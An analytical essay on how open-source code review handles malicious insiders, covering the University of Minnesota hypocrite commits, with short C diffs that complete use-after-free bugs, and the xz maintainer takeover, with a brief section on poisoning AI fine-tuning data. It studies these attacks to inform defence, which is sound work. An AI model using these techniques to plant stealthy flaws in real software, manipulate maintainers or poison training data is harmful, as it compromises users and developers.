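# Open-source code review and patient insiders: the hypocrite commits, the xz backdoor and the lessons for reviewing AI training

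## How open-source code review works and whom it trusts

Anyone may read, copy and change the source code of open-source software, and people who have never met often write it together. One person proposes a change, and another decides whether the project should accept it. In code review, someone other than the author reads the change before it becomes part of the program. Review mostly catches honest mistakes, but it could also stop someone who means harm, and two well-known cases tested whether it can. In 2020 researchers at the University of Minnesota sent deliberately flawed changes to the Linux kernel, the core of the Linux operating system. In 2024 it emerged that a maintainer of xz, a compression library, had hidden a backdoor in it after more than two years of useful work. Developers of AI models face a version of the same problem, because a colleague with bad intentions could change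 the files they share.

A *patch* is a proposed change to source code, and a *commit* is the same change once the project has recorded it in its history. The reviewer reads a *diff*, a line-by-line display of what the patch adds and removes, with a few neighbouring lines for context. A *maintainer* is a person with the right to accept patches into a project and usually to publish its releases. A *backdoor* is hidden code that gives its author access others do not have. An attacker need not write anything so explicit, though. An ordinary-looking bug will often do, and in C, the language of most of the kernel, a classic one is the *use-after-free*, in which a program goes on using memory it has already released. Here is a diff that creates one (the plus sign marks the added line):

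```
  struct session *s = open_session(user);
+ free(s);
  write_log(s->name);
```

The program opens a session and sets aside memory for it. The new line frees that memory, but the line after it still reads from it. By then the system may have given the same memory to another part of the program. An attacker who can choose what is stored there can feed the program false data and, in bad cases, take control of it. The error is easy to see when the three lines are side by side, but in a real program the last line may be in a different file. The diff then shows only a new call to `free`, which looks like a fix for a memory leak. The Minnesota researchers' patches relied on this sort of gap. Each fixed something minor while completing the conditions for a serious flaw.

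### From an email to a user's machine

The Linux kernel's developers document their procedure in detail, so a kernel patch is a good example of how review works. Corbet (2026), in *Development statistics for 6.19*, counted 14,344 changes from 2,141 developers in the February 2026 release, including 333 first-time contributors.

Suppose a newcomer finds a small memory leak in a network driver. She writes a fix and emails it to the driver's maintainer and a public mailing list. The Linux kernel documentation's *Submitting patches* requires one logical change per patch, sent as plain text so that others can quote and discuss single lines. The reviewer therefore receives a written argument that a problem exists, followed by a diff. The newcomer also includes a Signed-off-by line, in which she certifies, under "a known identity", that she has the right to submit the code. This is her own statement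 about licensing.

Anyone on the list may reply to a patch, and comments typically arrive within two or three weeks. Luck partly determines which experts read it. The main kernel list can carry 500 messages a day, according to the Linux kernel documentation's *How the development process works*, and a number of developers have stopped following it. A satisfied reader may offer a Reviewed-by line, which certifies that they have done a technical review and know of no issues that would count against the patch. An Acked-by line is weaker and records approval, sometimes of only part of the patch.

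AI tools now also review Linux patches. *Lessons from building Sashiko, an agentic code review system* (Gushchin and Brewer, 2026) describes an AI reviewer that a Google team built to help Linux maintainers catch bugs. It can take patches straight from the mailing lists, according to The Decoder's *Linus Torvalds tells AI critics in the Linux kernel community to fork*. Gushchin has claimed that it found 53 per cent of a set of 1,000 recent bugs, all of which human reviewers had missed, according to ETN's *Tekoäly tarkistaa nyt Linux-ytimen koodia*. *Linux Kernel Drops AI Tag Requirement, Uses Meta AI For Code Reviews* (Posch, 2026) reported that by October 2026 the kernel project was also using Meta AI for reviews. These tools do not replace the human signature, and in May 2026 Krzysztof Kozlowski amended the kernel documentation's *submitting patches* page to clarify that a "reviewer" is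 a person.

The driver's maintainer then decides whether to accept the patch. If he does, he copies it into his own version of the kernel source and adds his sign-off. He has seen the email, the replies and the diff, but he may have read them in a hurry. According to Corbet's figures, one networking maintainer, Jakub Kicinski, signed off 991 patches by other people in a 70-day cycle, or about 14 a day.

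From there the patch goes into linux-next, a preview of the coming kernel, where testers check whether it builds and whether it conflicts with other people's work. During a two-week merge window, Linus Torvalds, who created Linux and is the only person able to merge into the main version, pulls in collections of patches from the maintainers below him. In an older release, 2.6.38, he personally chose 112 of more than 9,500 patches. He sometimes looks closely, but he usually trusts his maintainers not to send him bad patches, and they trust the maintainers below them in the same way. Kernel developers call this the chain of trust. It probably means that a patch is read carefully once, near the bottom, and that people further up judge it mainly by who sent it.

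After the merge, developers spend six to ten weeks stabilising the kernel, mainly by looking for regressions, which are things that used to work and no longer do. This testing is unlikely to catch a hidden flaw that breaks nothing. A separate team then copies significant bug fixes back into kernels already in use. Most Linux machines run those kernels, or a vendor's variant that takes only selected patches, so a patch that passes for a bug fix can reach users sooner than a new feature.

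Most open-source projects are far smaller and work through a website such as GitHub. The contributor opens a *pull request*, a page with the description, the diff and a comment thread, and a maintainer reads it and presses a button to merge the change. Some projects keep a file that lists "code owners", the people responsible for reviewing changes to particular files. In the sample of *Automated Code Review Assignments* (2025), a code owner had reviewed, approved or merged the pull request under study in only about 42 per cent of the repositories where the file covers much of the code, and in 38 per cent of those where it covers little.

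Review usually ends at the merge, but users do not install the merged code directly. A maintainer packs the project into a *release tarball*, an archive that others download and build, or uploads a package to a registry, a public store such as PyPI for Python or npm for JavaScript. Linux distributions and other programs get it from there, and it reaches users as an update. The package may differ from the code that reviewers read. Imtiaz and Williams (2022), in *Are your dependencies code reviewed?*, compared 24,944 updates of heavily downloaded packages with their source repositories and found that 20.1 per cent contained at least one file absent from the repository. The causes they identified were innocent (build tools generate files, and people include files by accident). Users see only a version number, and even if they checked the files, an unexplained one would be a weak warning sign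 because a fifth of updates have one.

### What reviewers look for

Kernel reviewers want a patch to fix a real problem correctly and in readable code. They will probably reject a patch with basic style errors before anyone reads it. They also consider security, but most seem to give it a fairly low priority.

The best evidence on whether reviewers look for security problems comes from Braz and Bacchelli (2022), who interviewed ten developers and surveyed 182 for *Software Security during Modern Code Review*. They told participants that the study was about code review, without mentioning security. Nine of the 182 mentioned security in answer to an open question about what they focus on, while 23 mentioned performance. When the respondents were then asked about vulnerabilities, 111 said they always consider them. Actual habits presumably lie somewhere between those numbers, because an open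 question captures only what comes to mind first, and few people admit to ignoring vulnerabilities once a researcher has mentioned them. The low number is more useful for judging a project's defences, since nobody prompts reviewers to think about security in daily work.

The most common reason respondents gave was lack of knowledge or training, which 44 mentioned. Nine said that vulnerabilities are subtle, so dangerous code does not look bad. Nine did not know the rest of the codebase well enough to see how a change interacts with it, which is the problem in the `free` example when the last line is elsewhere. Eight pointed to third-party libraries, whose code the reviewer may never see, and six to lack of time. The interviews also showed something the survey had not. Seven of the ten developers assumed that another team or another part of the system handled security, with front-end and back-end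 developers each pointing to the other side. One, who writes mostly internal code, gives security about three seconds of thought. Only 43 of the 182 survey respondents felt that leaders acknowledge developers who do secure reviews.

Nearly all the respondents had jobs, and the researchers found them through web forums, social media and their own contacts, so the figures fit company teams better than volunteer projects. Volunteers are unlikely to have more time. One kernel reviewer gave up memory-management duties because of the volume of AI-generated patches, according to Tom's Hardware's *Linux kernel reviewer steps down from memory management duties*.

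### Three levels of trust

All of this assumes that somebody reads the patch, and whether anybody does depends a good deal on who sent it.

An unknown outsider has no standing, so a maintainer has to accept the patch. This means at least one person besides the author sees it, and that person has no obligation to the author. But the maintainer knows little about the outsider beyond an email address and a sign-off line, and it is normal for newcomers to contribute once and disappear. Corbet found that 36 per cent of the 5,424 people who first contributed to the Linux kernel during the 5.x series never appeared in another release.

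A maintainer still has to decide whether to accept each new patch from a known contributor, but the contributor's history of accepted patches is a reason to read it faster. This effect is hard to measure. The case for it rests on maintainers' workload and on the fact that maintainers further up the chain routinely accept patches based on trust in the sender. Some reviewers also work at the same company as the author. Statistics on the netdev mailing list (2024), where the kernel's networking developers work, show that a record 71 per cent of applied patches had review tags, or 57.5 per cent when reviewers from the author's company are excluded. For about one patch in seven, the only recorded reviewers were the author's colleagues.

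Maintainers can accept patches, including their own. In 2018, in the Ksummit-discuss mailing list's *Bug-introducing patches* thread, a kernel maintainer wrote that he sometimes applies his own patches without Reviewed-by tags because nobody cares enough about the driver to review them. A commenter on LWN, a Linux news site, described a milder practice in KVM, the kernel's virtualisation code, where a maintainer posts a trivial patch publicly, waits a few days and takes silence for consent. Both practices are understandable, since the fix would often never go in otherwise, but they limit what can be learned from the review records. In the 6.19 kernel, 56 per cent of patches carried a Reviewed-by tag. A missing tag means little when a maintainer applied somebody else's patch, because the maintainer presumably looked at it, but when maintainers applied their own patches, it may mean that nobody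 else looked at them.

Review is less complete outside the kernel. Imtiaz and Williams measured the share of changed code in each package update that had been reviewed, counting code as reviewed even if a second account had only merged or committed it. The median was 27.2 per cent. In 29.7 per cent of packages no update had any reviewed code, and in 9 per cent every update was fully reviewed. These figures date from 2021 and are somewhat low because they miss reviews done outside GitHub. Updates tended to have either almost all or almost none of their changed code reviewed, which the researchers attribute to small groups of maintainers reviewing outsiders' work but not their own. Eight of the maintainers who disputed the results replied that the measure made no sense for them because they had no colleague to ask for a review.

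A *patient insider* deliberately rises through these levels by doing real, useful work to obtain legitimate access, and then misuses it. An outsider has to get a bad patch past a reviewer, but a patient insider keeps contributing until their changes may no longer be reviewed, and by then they often have the right to build the release as well. Stealing a maintainer's password gives an attacker the same access without the work, but the account's owner may notice. An honest maintainer who turns against a project after years is also a danger, but did not seek access in order to misuse it.

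Imtiaz and Williams wrote in 2022 that several maintainers could develop a package together, wait for it to become popular, and then add a backdoor. The xz case fits this fairly well, except that the attacker joined an existing project. The standard remedy is to require two trusted people to vouch for every change. That does not help if both are in on the plan, and a rogue maintainer can also open a pull request from a second account and approve it from the first.

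### The same question for AI training

People who train AI models also have shared files to protect. A *fine-tuning dataset* is a set of examples, often requests paired with the desired answers, that developers use to adjust a model's behaviour after its initial training. A *training run* is one execution of the training process, including its data, settings, code and saved versions of the model. Employees and contractors need access to both to do their jobs. One of them could plant examples that teach the model a behaviour its developer did not intend. Researchers call this *data poisoning*. The resulting backdoor would be hidden in the trained model and would not appear in any line of code. A diff of the dataset would show the planted examples, but they would look like ordinary text among thousands of other examples. What could a reviewer see if someone with legitimate access changed the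 data or the run?

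## The University of Minnesota hypocrite commits

In 2020 Qiushi Wu and Kangjie Lu, computer scientists at the University of Minnesota (UMN), wanted to learn whether an outsider could get a serious vulnerability past the Linux kernel's reviewers. Their group knew the process well and had contributed roughly 400 bug fixes since 2018. For *On the Feasibility of Stealthily Introducing Vulnerabilities in Open-Source Software*, Wu and Lu studied old kernel vulnerabilities and also sent the kernel's developers flawed patches of their own. The patches made the paper notorious, but the study of old vulnerabilities is better evidence about review.

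### A one-line fix that completed a vulnerability

Wu and Lu explain their method with an honest mistake from the kernel's history. The kernel manages many objects by *reference counting*. It counts how many parts of the program are using an object, each part lowers the count when it has finished, and the kernel frees the object when the count reaches zero. If one part forgets to lower the count, the object stays in memory for good. Somebody noticed what looked like such a leak in code that registers a component of network hardware, and added one line (the code is shortened):

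```
  err = device_register(&bus->dev);
  if (err) {
      pr_err("mii_bus %s failed to register\n", bus->id);
+     put_device(&bus->dev);
      return -EINVAL;
  }
```

The function `put_device` lowers the reference count by one. When registration fails, the new line drops the last reference, so the count reaches zero and the kernel frees `bus`, although no function with "free" in its name appears in the diff. The code then returns an error, and another part of the kernel cleans up by calling `mdiobus_free()`, which uses `bus` and frees it again. This use-after-free stayed in the kernel for five years and is now listed as CVE-2019-12819 (a CVE number identifies a vulnerability in a public catalogue).

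To spot the problem, a reviewer would have had to know that this was the last reference and that the caller would also clean up, neither of which the diff showed. The line itself is what a careful programmer would be expected to write.

A use-after-free occurs when a program frees memory and then uses it. Before the patch, this code used the memory but did not free it early. Wu and Lu call such a flaw an *immature vulnerability*, meaning that the code already meets some but not all of the necessary conditions. A *hypocrite commit* is a small patch that fixes a minor problem while adding the missing conditions for a serious vulnerability. They count a patch as small if it changes fewer than 30 lines and adds no feature. The minor problem has to be real, because it gives the maintainer a reason to accept the patch.

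Kernel developers do not usually remove immature vulnerabilities. They told Wu and Lu that they fix code only when it goes wrong. This is defensible, since the code is not yet wrong and extra checks would slow it down and take time to review, but it leaves an attacker many candidates to exploit. Wu and Lu's tools flagged more than 6,000 immature use-after-frees, though this is the raw output of an automated search. One researcher checked 200 of them by hand and picked three within a week.

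The paper assumes an attacker who is neither a developer nor a maintainer of the project, can send only small changes, and must get each one through review by honest maintainers. It therefore covers newcomers but not patient insiders, even though maintainers also introduced vulnerabilities by mistake in its own data. They wrote 47.8 per cent of a sample of 500 recent small patches, and 37.3 per cent of the small patches that had introduced vulnerabilities.

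### Where reviewers miss memory errors

For the historical study, Wu and Lu took the kernel vulnerabilities with CVE numbers for which they could find both the patch that introduced the flaw and the patch that fixed it. Small patches had introduced 138 of these vulnerabilities, or 9.8 per cent. The people who wrote those patches introduced the flaws by mistake, and reviewers missed them.

Wu and Lu then looked for features that made the mistakes hard to see. Many were in *error paths*, the code that runs only after something has gone wrong. Testers rarely trigger those paths, and reviewers expect to find cleanup calls there. Other mistakes involved functions whose names give no hint that they release memory, such as `put_device`. The kernel has at least 457 functions that release memory, and more than half lack a word such as "release" in the name. Some flaws involved *aliases*, two names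 for the same piece of memory, so a programmer could free it under one name and keep using it under the other. Others involved indirect calls, where the function to be called is not fixed until the program runs, so a reader of the diff cannot easily tell which code will run.

The hardest cases involved concurrency, where two pieces of code run at the same time and an error appears only if their steps interleave in a particular way. One patch to a USB driver moved a single line, which marks a device as gone, from just below a lock to just above it. A second function could then see the mark and free the device while the first function was still using it. A reviewer can't see this from the moved line alone and has to work out what every other function might be doing at that moment.

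To measure how often reviewers catch such flaws, Wu and Lu collected a separate set of use-after-free errors from January 2015 to August 2020. Some had been merged and discovered later, and others had been blocked by maintainers in review. They defined the *catch rate* as

catch rate = N_C / (N_C + N_E)

where N_C is the number of flaws that maintainers caught and N_E the number that evaded them and came to light afterwards.

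| What the flaw involved | Catch rate |
|---|---|
| Baseline | 56.6% |
| Error paths | 42.0% |
| Aliases | 38.4% |
| Implicit release of memory | 36.3% |
| Concurrency | 19.4% |

The paper includes only nine cases involving indirect calls, and maintainers caught five of them. It gives no case counts for the other rows, so we can't calculate their margins of error.

Wu and Lu describe the rates as upper bounds. They argue that some merged flaws are still undiscovered, so the true N_E is larger and the true catch rate lower. This would follow if they had found every blocked patch, but they almost certainly did not. A patch that fails in review leaves only an email thread. The reviewer may have turned it down for another reason, asked for a rewrite that happened to remove the flaw, or described the problem in words that a search for use-after-free errors would miss.

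Suppose the researchers found a share *a* of the flaws that reviewers blocked and a share *b* of the flaws that got through. The observed ratio N_C/N_E is then *a/b* times the true ratio, so the published rate is an upper bound only if *a* is at least as large as *b*. If they found 80 per cent of the blocked flaws and half of the others, the true baseline is about 45 per cent. If they found half of the blocked flaws and 80 per cent of the others, it is about 68 per cent. The paper doesn't estimate either share.

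The ranking of the features is also less certain than it looks in the table. As a second measure, Wu and Lu compared how long merged flaws survived before someone fixed them. Concurrency was the stealthiest feature on both measures. Error paths ranked second by survival time but have the highest catch rate of the four features in the table. This may be because survival depends on testing as well as review, and a flaw in code that rarely runs can last a long time even if a reviewer would have spotted it fairly easily.

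It is unclear how these rates carry over to deliberate flaws. An attacker can target code that involves concurrency, which should lower the odds of being caught, and can try again after a rejection. But many of the honest mistakes came from people the reviewers knew, and a stranger's patch may get a closer reading. The live experiment could in principle have helped settle this.

### Five patches under two false names

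Wu and Lu prepared patches of fewer than five lines for three immature vulnerabilities. One added an error message, one fixed a memory leak and one corrected a reference count. The reference-count patch looked roughly like this (they simplified the code so that readers could not trace it):

```
  if (ret < 0) {
+     put_device(devA);
      dev_err(&devA->dev, "error message.");
```

The added line may free `devA`, and the line below it uses `devA` to print a message. Both lines are visible here, but a reader needs to know that `put_device` can free a device to see the flaw.

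The researchers say they sent the patches from a random Gmail account and waited for a maintainer to reply with something like "looks good". They would then immediately point out the flaw, ask the maintainer not to apply the patch, and supply a correct one. They report that in all three cases the maintainers confirmed they would not go ahead with the flawed patch, and that none of the flawed patches became a commit. They conclude that the attack is practical, but as Derek Jones noted on his blog, The Shape of Code, they never say how many of the three patches passed review.

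The Linux Foundation is the non-profit that supports kernel development, and its Technical Advisory Board (TAB) is a panel of ten people, mostly kernel developers. The board reconstructed what happened from the public mailing lists and from a disclosure that the researchers made in April 2021. The TAB's *Report on University of Minnesota Breach-of-Trust Incident* (2021) lists five patches, here in the order in which they were sent:

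| Sent (UTC) | Sender's name | First reply | What happened |
|---|---|---|---|
| 4 August 2020 | James Bond | None | Ordinary bug fix, sent from the wrong account; the maintainer ignored it |
| 9 August | James Bond | 7 hours | Maintainers recognised a copy of an older bad patch and rejected it |
| 21 August | George Acosta | 7 days | Valid; the maintainer accepted it |
| 21 August | George Acosta | 4.5 hours | A reviewer saw that it was wrong and suggested a correction; the sender did not follow it up |
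| 21 August | James Bond | 6 days | The maintainer found it wrong; the sender apologised |

The accepted patch added an error message to the driver for an encryption chip. Wu and Lu believed that it created a use-after-free, but they had misunderstood how the kernel manages devices of this type, and the patch was harmless. They learned this when they asked about it after the maintainer had accepted it. The TAB could not explain why their paper still presented it as an incorrect change. Their assurance that no flawed patch became a commit is accurate, but partly because the accepted patch did not contain the flaw they intended.

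The other three hypocrite commits did contain real bugs, and maintainers accepted none of them. The TAB concluded that the review process had worked as intended. It was to some extent judging its own members' work, since they included Greg Kroah-Hartman, who maintains the stable kernel releases and had started the ban on the university. Corbet (2021), in *An update on the UMN affair*, was more guarded, writing that the planted bugs were not always the reason for rejection (quoted in Slashdot's *Linux Stops Reverting Most University of Minnesota Patches, Admits Good Faith*). Luck also helped keep the patches out. The 9 August patch repeated a mistake that had already inspired a conference talk, and the maintainer who received the 4 August patch ignored it because developers had by then worked out that "James Bond" was a false name.

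Three attempts are too few to show how often an attacker would succeed. If each flawed patch had a 63 per cent chance of getting through, all three would still fail about one time in twenty, so the result does not rule out a success rate that high. It is also consistent with Wu and Lu's own baseline, since reviewers who catch 56.6 per cent of flaws would catch three out of three about 18 per cent of the time. The patches were not a random sample, because one researcher chose them by hand, and Wu and Lu concede that the flaws might not have been exploitable. Jones thought the paper should have been about the history of accidental vulnerabilities, and the numbers support his view. A proper test would need far more patches and a controlled setting.

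The experiment did show that a patch signed with an invented name can enter the kernel's history. The patch stayed there for eight months, until the researchers disclosed it. The maintainer had no practical way to check the name on the sign-off, and the patch was good.

### The dispute over consent

The IEEE Symposium on Security and Privacy, a leading security conference, accepted the paper in November 2020. Lu shared the abstract on Twitter, and objections came within a day or so. On 1 December, in *Ethics concerns about paper accepted for publication*, Linderud, Torres-Arias and two colleagues asked the conference's chairs to reconsider. They wrote that the researchers had experimented on open-source developers without any sign of approval from an institutional review board (IRB), the committee that oversees a university's research on people. They also feared that exploitable code had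 reached the kernel, and that automated tools might copy it into older versions without the later corrections. That fear proved unfounded, but nobody outside the research group could have known this at the time because the group had not said which patches were involved.

Wu and Lu (2020) replied two weeks later in *Clarifications on the “hypocrite commit” work (FAQ)*. They had not applied to the IRB before the experiment because they did not think of it as research on people. The board reviewed it afterwards, agreed and issued an exemption letter. They argued that they had studied the patching process, had written to a community rather than to individuals, and had collected no personal data. They apologised for wasting maintainers' time.

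The researchers' claim that they had written only to a community is hard to accept, because individual people read the patches. One of them spent time teaching an apparent beginner how to fix a bad patch. The TAB singled this out as especially hurtful, because the researchers knew the patch was bad and reviewers' time is the kernel community's scarcest resource. René Mayrhofer, who had signed the letter to the conference, argued in the comments on LWN's *The TAB report on the UMN affair* (2021) that wasted time counts as harm, and that researchers who deceive their subjects need an independent committee to oversee them. In the same thread Ted Ts'o, a kernel developer and TAB member, suggested that the university could hardly concede the point, because a federal grant had paid for the work and the grant's rules on human subjects would then have applied.

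Some readers thought the outrage was overdone. One commenter on LWN compared the experiment to the fake phishing emails that companies send to their own staff. Another answered that a senior manager approves those tests and that employees accept monitoring as a condition of using the company's systems. That approval and consent seem to be the real difference. Greg KH (2021), as Kroah-Hartman signs his emails, made a similar point about television prank shows, where the people involved agree to the broadcast afterwards. Wu and Lu could have asked a few senior kernel developers for permission without warning the reviewers, and in their later apology they said it was a mistake not to have found a way to do so. A company could more easily run this kind of test on the people who review its training data, because it can authorise the test itself.

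### The ban and the apology

In April 2021, after seven months of silence, members of the group sent the kernel a new batch of poor patches. Edge (2021), in *Intentionally buggy commits for fame—and papers*, reported that two developers had questioned one of them, a change to the kernel's network file system. Kroah-Hartman took the batch for another experiment. In a message to the sender, reproduced in AskWoody's *Linux banned University of Minnesota for sending buggy patches*, he recalled the earlier paper and asked, "what am I supposed to think of such a thing?" On 20 April he told developers to reject everything from the university's addresses, and the next day he posted 190 patches to undo its earlier work.

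The department's leaders said they had learned the details of the research only that day, according to text that Cutler (2021) quoted on a security mailing list. The researchers apologised on 24 April and withdrew the paper two days later. In *An open letter to the Linux community* they explained that the April patches came from a separate project, which used a tool to find bugs that other people's patches had introduced. In its *Statement from Computer Science & Engineering confirming Linux Technical Advisory Board findings* (2021), the University of Minnesota repeated that the April patches were sent in good faith but conceded that they were superfluous and of poor quality. It counted four hypocrite commits in all, one of them valid, and said that no other project had received any.

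So the patches that set off the ban were bad but submitted in good faith, and Kroah-Hartman had guessed wrong about their purpose. His guess was reasonable, since an honest bad patch and a planted one can look the same and the group had already deceived reviewers once. The kernel developers could have corrected themselves sooner. One of them, Pavel Machek, objected that there had been no deception in 2021 and that his own side was still spreading inaccurate information at the end of April. Some commenters on LWN also complained that one maintainer had banned a whole university and created a lot of review work for everyone else. Jan Engelhardt wrote to the security list that he expected the harsh response to teach future researchers to hide better.

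The two sides reconciled fairly quickly. Cook (2021), replying for the kernel developers, thanked the group for its years of bug fixes, and the TAB recommended that an experienced developer at the university check patches before anyone there submits them.

### An accidental audit of 435 commits

Kernel developers re-examined all of the university's earlier patches because nobody could be sure which had been submitted in good faith. Within about two weeks they had reviewed 435 commits, most of them from earlier bug-finding projects. The TAB's report thanks 85 people, by one reader's count. The re-examination was an unplanned test of review, much larger than the experiment that caused it.

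The reviewers judged 349 commits correct and 39 in need of fixing. Other developers had already fixed or reverted 25 more. Another 12 no longer mattered because the kernel had dropped the code, 9 were old commits by people unconnected with the group, and one author had asked for his own commit to be removed. One of the 39 was the valid error-message patch, which had to be removed only because of its false name. The other 38, the 25 and the withdrawn commit make 64 wrong commits out of 435, or about 15 per cent. In the open letter, as quoted in Slashdot's *University of Minnesota Researchers Send Apology to Linux Kernel Mailing List*, the researchers had described 190 of these patches as "all correct", as far as they could discern.

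The TAB labelled each commit with the research project it came from, and the error rate varied widely between projects. Two projects looked for places where the kernel fails to check whether an operation has succeeded, and 47 of their roughly 164 commits (29 per cent) were wrong. Four other projects produced about 185 commits, of which 9 (5 per cent) were wrong. The 15 per cent is therefore an average over quite different kinds of patch, and applying it to the kernel as a whole would be risky.

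The titles of the later corrections indicate what went wrong. One patch to the driver for Thunderbolt, a type of cable connection, made the code stop if a certain call failed. Another developer later fixed a memory leak that occurred when that call failed, presumably because the new exit skipped the cleanup. This resembles a hypocrite commit, because a small, sensible fix in an error path introduced a different problem. Ts'o (2021) jokingly called such patches "good faith hypocrite commits" and suggested that the researchers study them to learn how reviewers could do better.

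The audit can't be used to calculate a catch rate because nobody counted how many of the group's bad patches reviewers had turned down. The TAB also did not sort the errors by seriousness, and many were probably harmless in practice. The audit's reviewers may also have missed some errors. They marked one reference-count fix as correct even though they noted that a later patch had to repair it.

The audit offers a rough check on Wu and Lu's claim that their published rates are upper bounds. Excluding the withdrawn commit, which was only weeks old, there were 63 wrong commits. Ordinary development had dealt with 25 of them, or 40 per cent, before the audit began, although most were about two years old by then. If use-after-free errors come to light at the same pace, *b* in the earlier calculation is 0.4, and the claim holds unless Wu and Lu overlooked more than 60 per cent of the blocked patches.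 If they overlooked none, the baseline would fall from 56.6 to about 34 per cent. Developers probably find use-after-frees faster than faulty error checks, because they are more serious and automated tools look for them, so the fall is likely to be smaller. Still, the claim looks more plausible than it did from the paper alone.

Corbet wrote, in a passage quoted in Tildes' *An update on the UMN affair*, that the kernel's process will not hold together if maintainers cannot generally trust the patches they receive. The audit was an attempt to do without that trust for one group of contributors, and it only partly worked. Eighty-five developers could find the faulty commits, but they relied largely on the researchers' own account and on whether a patch matched one of the group's published bug lists to decide which were deliberate. A patient insider would have given no such account, and a single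 planted flaw would have been one of more than sixty mistakes.

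## How the xz attacker became a maintainer

The Minnesota researchers sent the kernel's maintainers patches as strangers, so a maintainer had to accept each one. A contributor to xz who used the name Jia Tan got past that requirement by doing useful work. After about 14 months, Jia Tan could change the code without anyone's approval, and soon afterwards could also publish releases.

Linux distributions use xz widely. Lasse Collin designed its file format with others between 2005 and 2008. By 2022 he was maintaining C and Java versions of the software as an unpaid hobby. About ten people were active in the project's chat channel.

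Russ Cox's *Timeline of the xz open source attack* (2024) compiled the dates within days of the backdoor's discovery. Przymus and Durieux's *Wolves in the Repository* (2025) later reconstructed the attack's history from 1,020 commits, 307 mailing-list messages and 2,944 GitHub events.

### Fourteen months to commit rights

Jia Tan's first patches were small and, even in retrospect, look harmless. One added a file of settings for text editors. The next fixed an apparent problem with reproducible builds, which give identical output from the same source so that others can check them. Cox dates the main steps as follows:

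| Date | Step | What Jia Tan gained |
|---|---|---|
| 29 October 2021 | Sends a first patch to the mailing list | A name the maintainer has seen |
| 7 February 2022 | Collin merges the first commit with Jia Tan's address as author | A record of accepted work |
| 29 June 2022 | Collin writes that Jia Tan is "practically a co-maintainer already" | Public standing |
| 28 October 2022 | Joins the project's organisation on GitHub | No rights yet, but a necessary step towards them |
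| 30 November 2022 | Collin has bug reports sent to both of them | A view of what users notice |
| 30 December 2022 | Merges a batch of commits directly | Changes no longer need a second reader |
| 18 March 2023 | Builds and publishes version 5.4.2 | Control over what users install |
| 19 January 2024 | Moves the website to GitHub | Control over the project's public page |

Przymus and Durieux give the same dates as Cox for the first patch and the website move, but they write that Jia Tan created the GitHub organisation on 12 December 2022, whereas Cox writes that Jia Tan joined it in October. The December date may apply only to the xz repository there. Whether Jia Tan created or joined the organisation matters a little, because whoever creates an organisation normally decides who else gets rights in it.

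They also put Jia Tan's first release on 13 December 2022, three months earlier than Cox. They may have counted the person who posted a release on GitHub, while Cox counted the person who built the archive. On his page *xz backdoor* (2024), Collin states that he and Jia Tan each signed the archives they had made, so the signature on the December release should settle it. (Przymus and Durieux also give the length of Jia Tan's involvement as 2.6 years, but their own first and last dates are about 2.4 years apart.)

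Until some point in 2022, Collin had to apply Jia Tan's patches himself, so a second person saw each one. The batch of 30 December is the first firm evidence that he no longer had to. Collin kept working on the code and could still read Jia Tan's commits, but they now took effect whether or not he read them. By March 2023, releases no longer had a second reader. Duo's *Carefully Crafted Campaign Led to XZ Utils Backdoor* quotes Feross Aboukhadijeh, who founded the security company Socket, as saying that the attack came from "the person who was legitimately authorized to publish".

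Two maintainers did look at one important change. In June 2023 a newcomer called Hans Jansen sent two patches that made a checksum calculation slightly faster, and the backdoor later relied on them. Collin reworked the code, and Jia Tan praised it and merged the final commit. This would have satisfied a rule that two trusted people must see every change, even though Jia Tan was the attacker and may also have been Jansen.

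### What the useful work bought

Przymus and Durieux count only eight malicious commits, all from 2024, among the hundreds Jia Tan made. The rest were mostly the ordinary work of a small project. Jia Tan mainly contributed code in 2022 and mainly did maintenance in 2023, such as updating translations and looking after the build system. Overall, Jia Tan changed more lines of documentation and translations than of source code.

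Some of Jia Tan's contributions probably took little effort. Jia Tan used a grammar checker to find typos and worked through warnings from a build tool. Przymus and Durieux also suspect that Jia Tan used automatic translation or copied from other projects, because the translations covered more languages than one person was likely to know. Reviewing other people's patches took more skill, and Przymus and Durieux judge that Jia Tan did it reasonably well even when the patches were complicated.

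The early patches gave Collin a reason to reply, and by late April 2022 he had merged four of them. The translations and documentation kept Jia Tan's name in the project's history and were unlikely to draw close scrutiny. Work on the tests made it normal for Jia Tan to add test files, where the attacker later hid malicious code.

Jia Tan became the person people wrote to by answering users' questions and announcing releases. When the project moved to GitHub, Jia Tan set up a bug report form that listed Jia Tan's address instead of Collin's. In March 2023, Jia Tan also became the contact for OSS-Fuzz, a Google service that looks for bugs by giving programs unusual input. Someone planning a backdoor would want to hear about bugs first, but a new maintainer taking over routine work would have made the same change.

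Work on other projects helped too. Securelist's *Assessing the Y, and How, of the XZ Utils incident*, by researchers at the security company Kaspersky, reports that Jia Tan contributed more than 500 patches to several projects. At least one of these may have been malicious. Schneier on Security's *XZ Utils Backdoor* quotes an Ars Technica report that the account's first known commit, in 2021, replaced a safe printing function in the libarchive project with a less secure one, and that nobody noticed at the time. The change resembles a hypocrite commit, but a careless beginner could also have made it.

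Jia Tan also came close to becoming a Linux kernel maintainer. On 20 March 2024 Collin sent the kernel's developers a patch set that listed him and Jia Tan as maintainers of the kernel's xz code. This would have brought Jia Tan into the kernel's chain of trust. Cox sees no sign that Collin meant any harm.

### The pressure on Lasse Collin

In the spring and summer of 2022, two people whom nobody on the mailing list seems to have known complained to Collin about his pace. Jigar Kumar wrote six times between 27 April and 22 June, according to the message headers Securelist reproduces (Cox dates the first to 22 April). Dennis Ens wrote twice.

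In his first three emails, Kumar complained that Collin had not yet merged a patch by Jia Tan. On 19 May Ens asked whether the Java version still had a maintainer. Collin apologised the same day and wrote that Jia Tan had been helping him off the mailing list and might have a bigger role in future. He added that "something has to change in the long term".

Kumar then became ruder. On 7 June he told Ens that nothing would happen until there was a new maintainer, because the current one had lost interest. Collin replied that he hadn't lost interest, but that long-term mental health problems, among other things, had limited his "ability to care", and he reminded them that xz was an unpaid hobby. A week later Kumar asked why Collin should wait for the next big release before changing maintainer. On 21 June Ens wrote that he was sorry about Collin's mental health and suggested that Collin hand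 over either the C or the Java version. The next day Kumar asked Jia Tan, "Why can't you commit this yourself?" On 29 June Collin answered that a change of maintainer was already in progress.

The pressure may have worked, as Cox concludes, but Collin had raised the idea of a bigger role for Jia Tan on 19 May, before either of the people pressing him had called for a new maintainer. He also told the list that he had long been thinking about finding a co-maintainer. The emails seem to have hurried him more than persuaded him. On 8 June he was writing "perhaps" and "we'll see", and three weeks later Jia Tan was practically a co-maintainer. Jia Tan's help off the list probably mattered as much, but outsiders can't see it. An LWN reader, helsleym (2024), suggested in a comment on *A backdoor in xz* that Jia Tan may have moved the conversation off the list for that reason.

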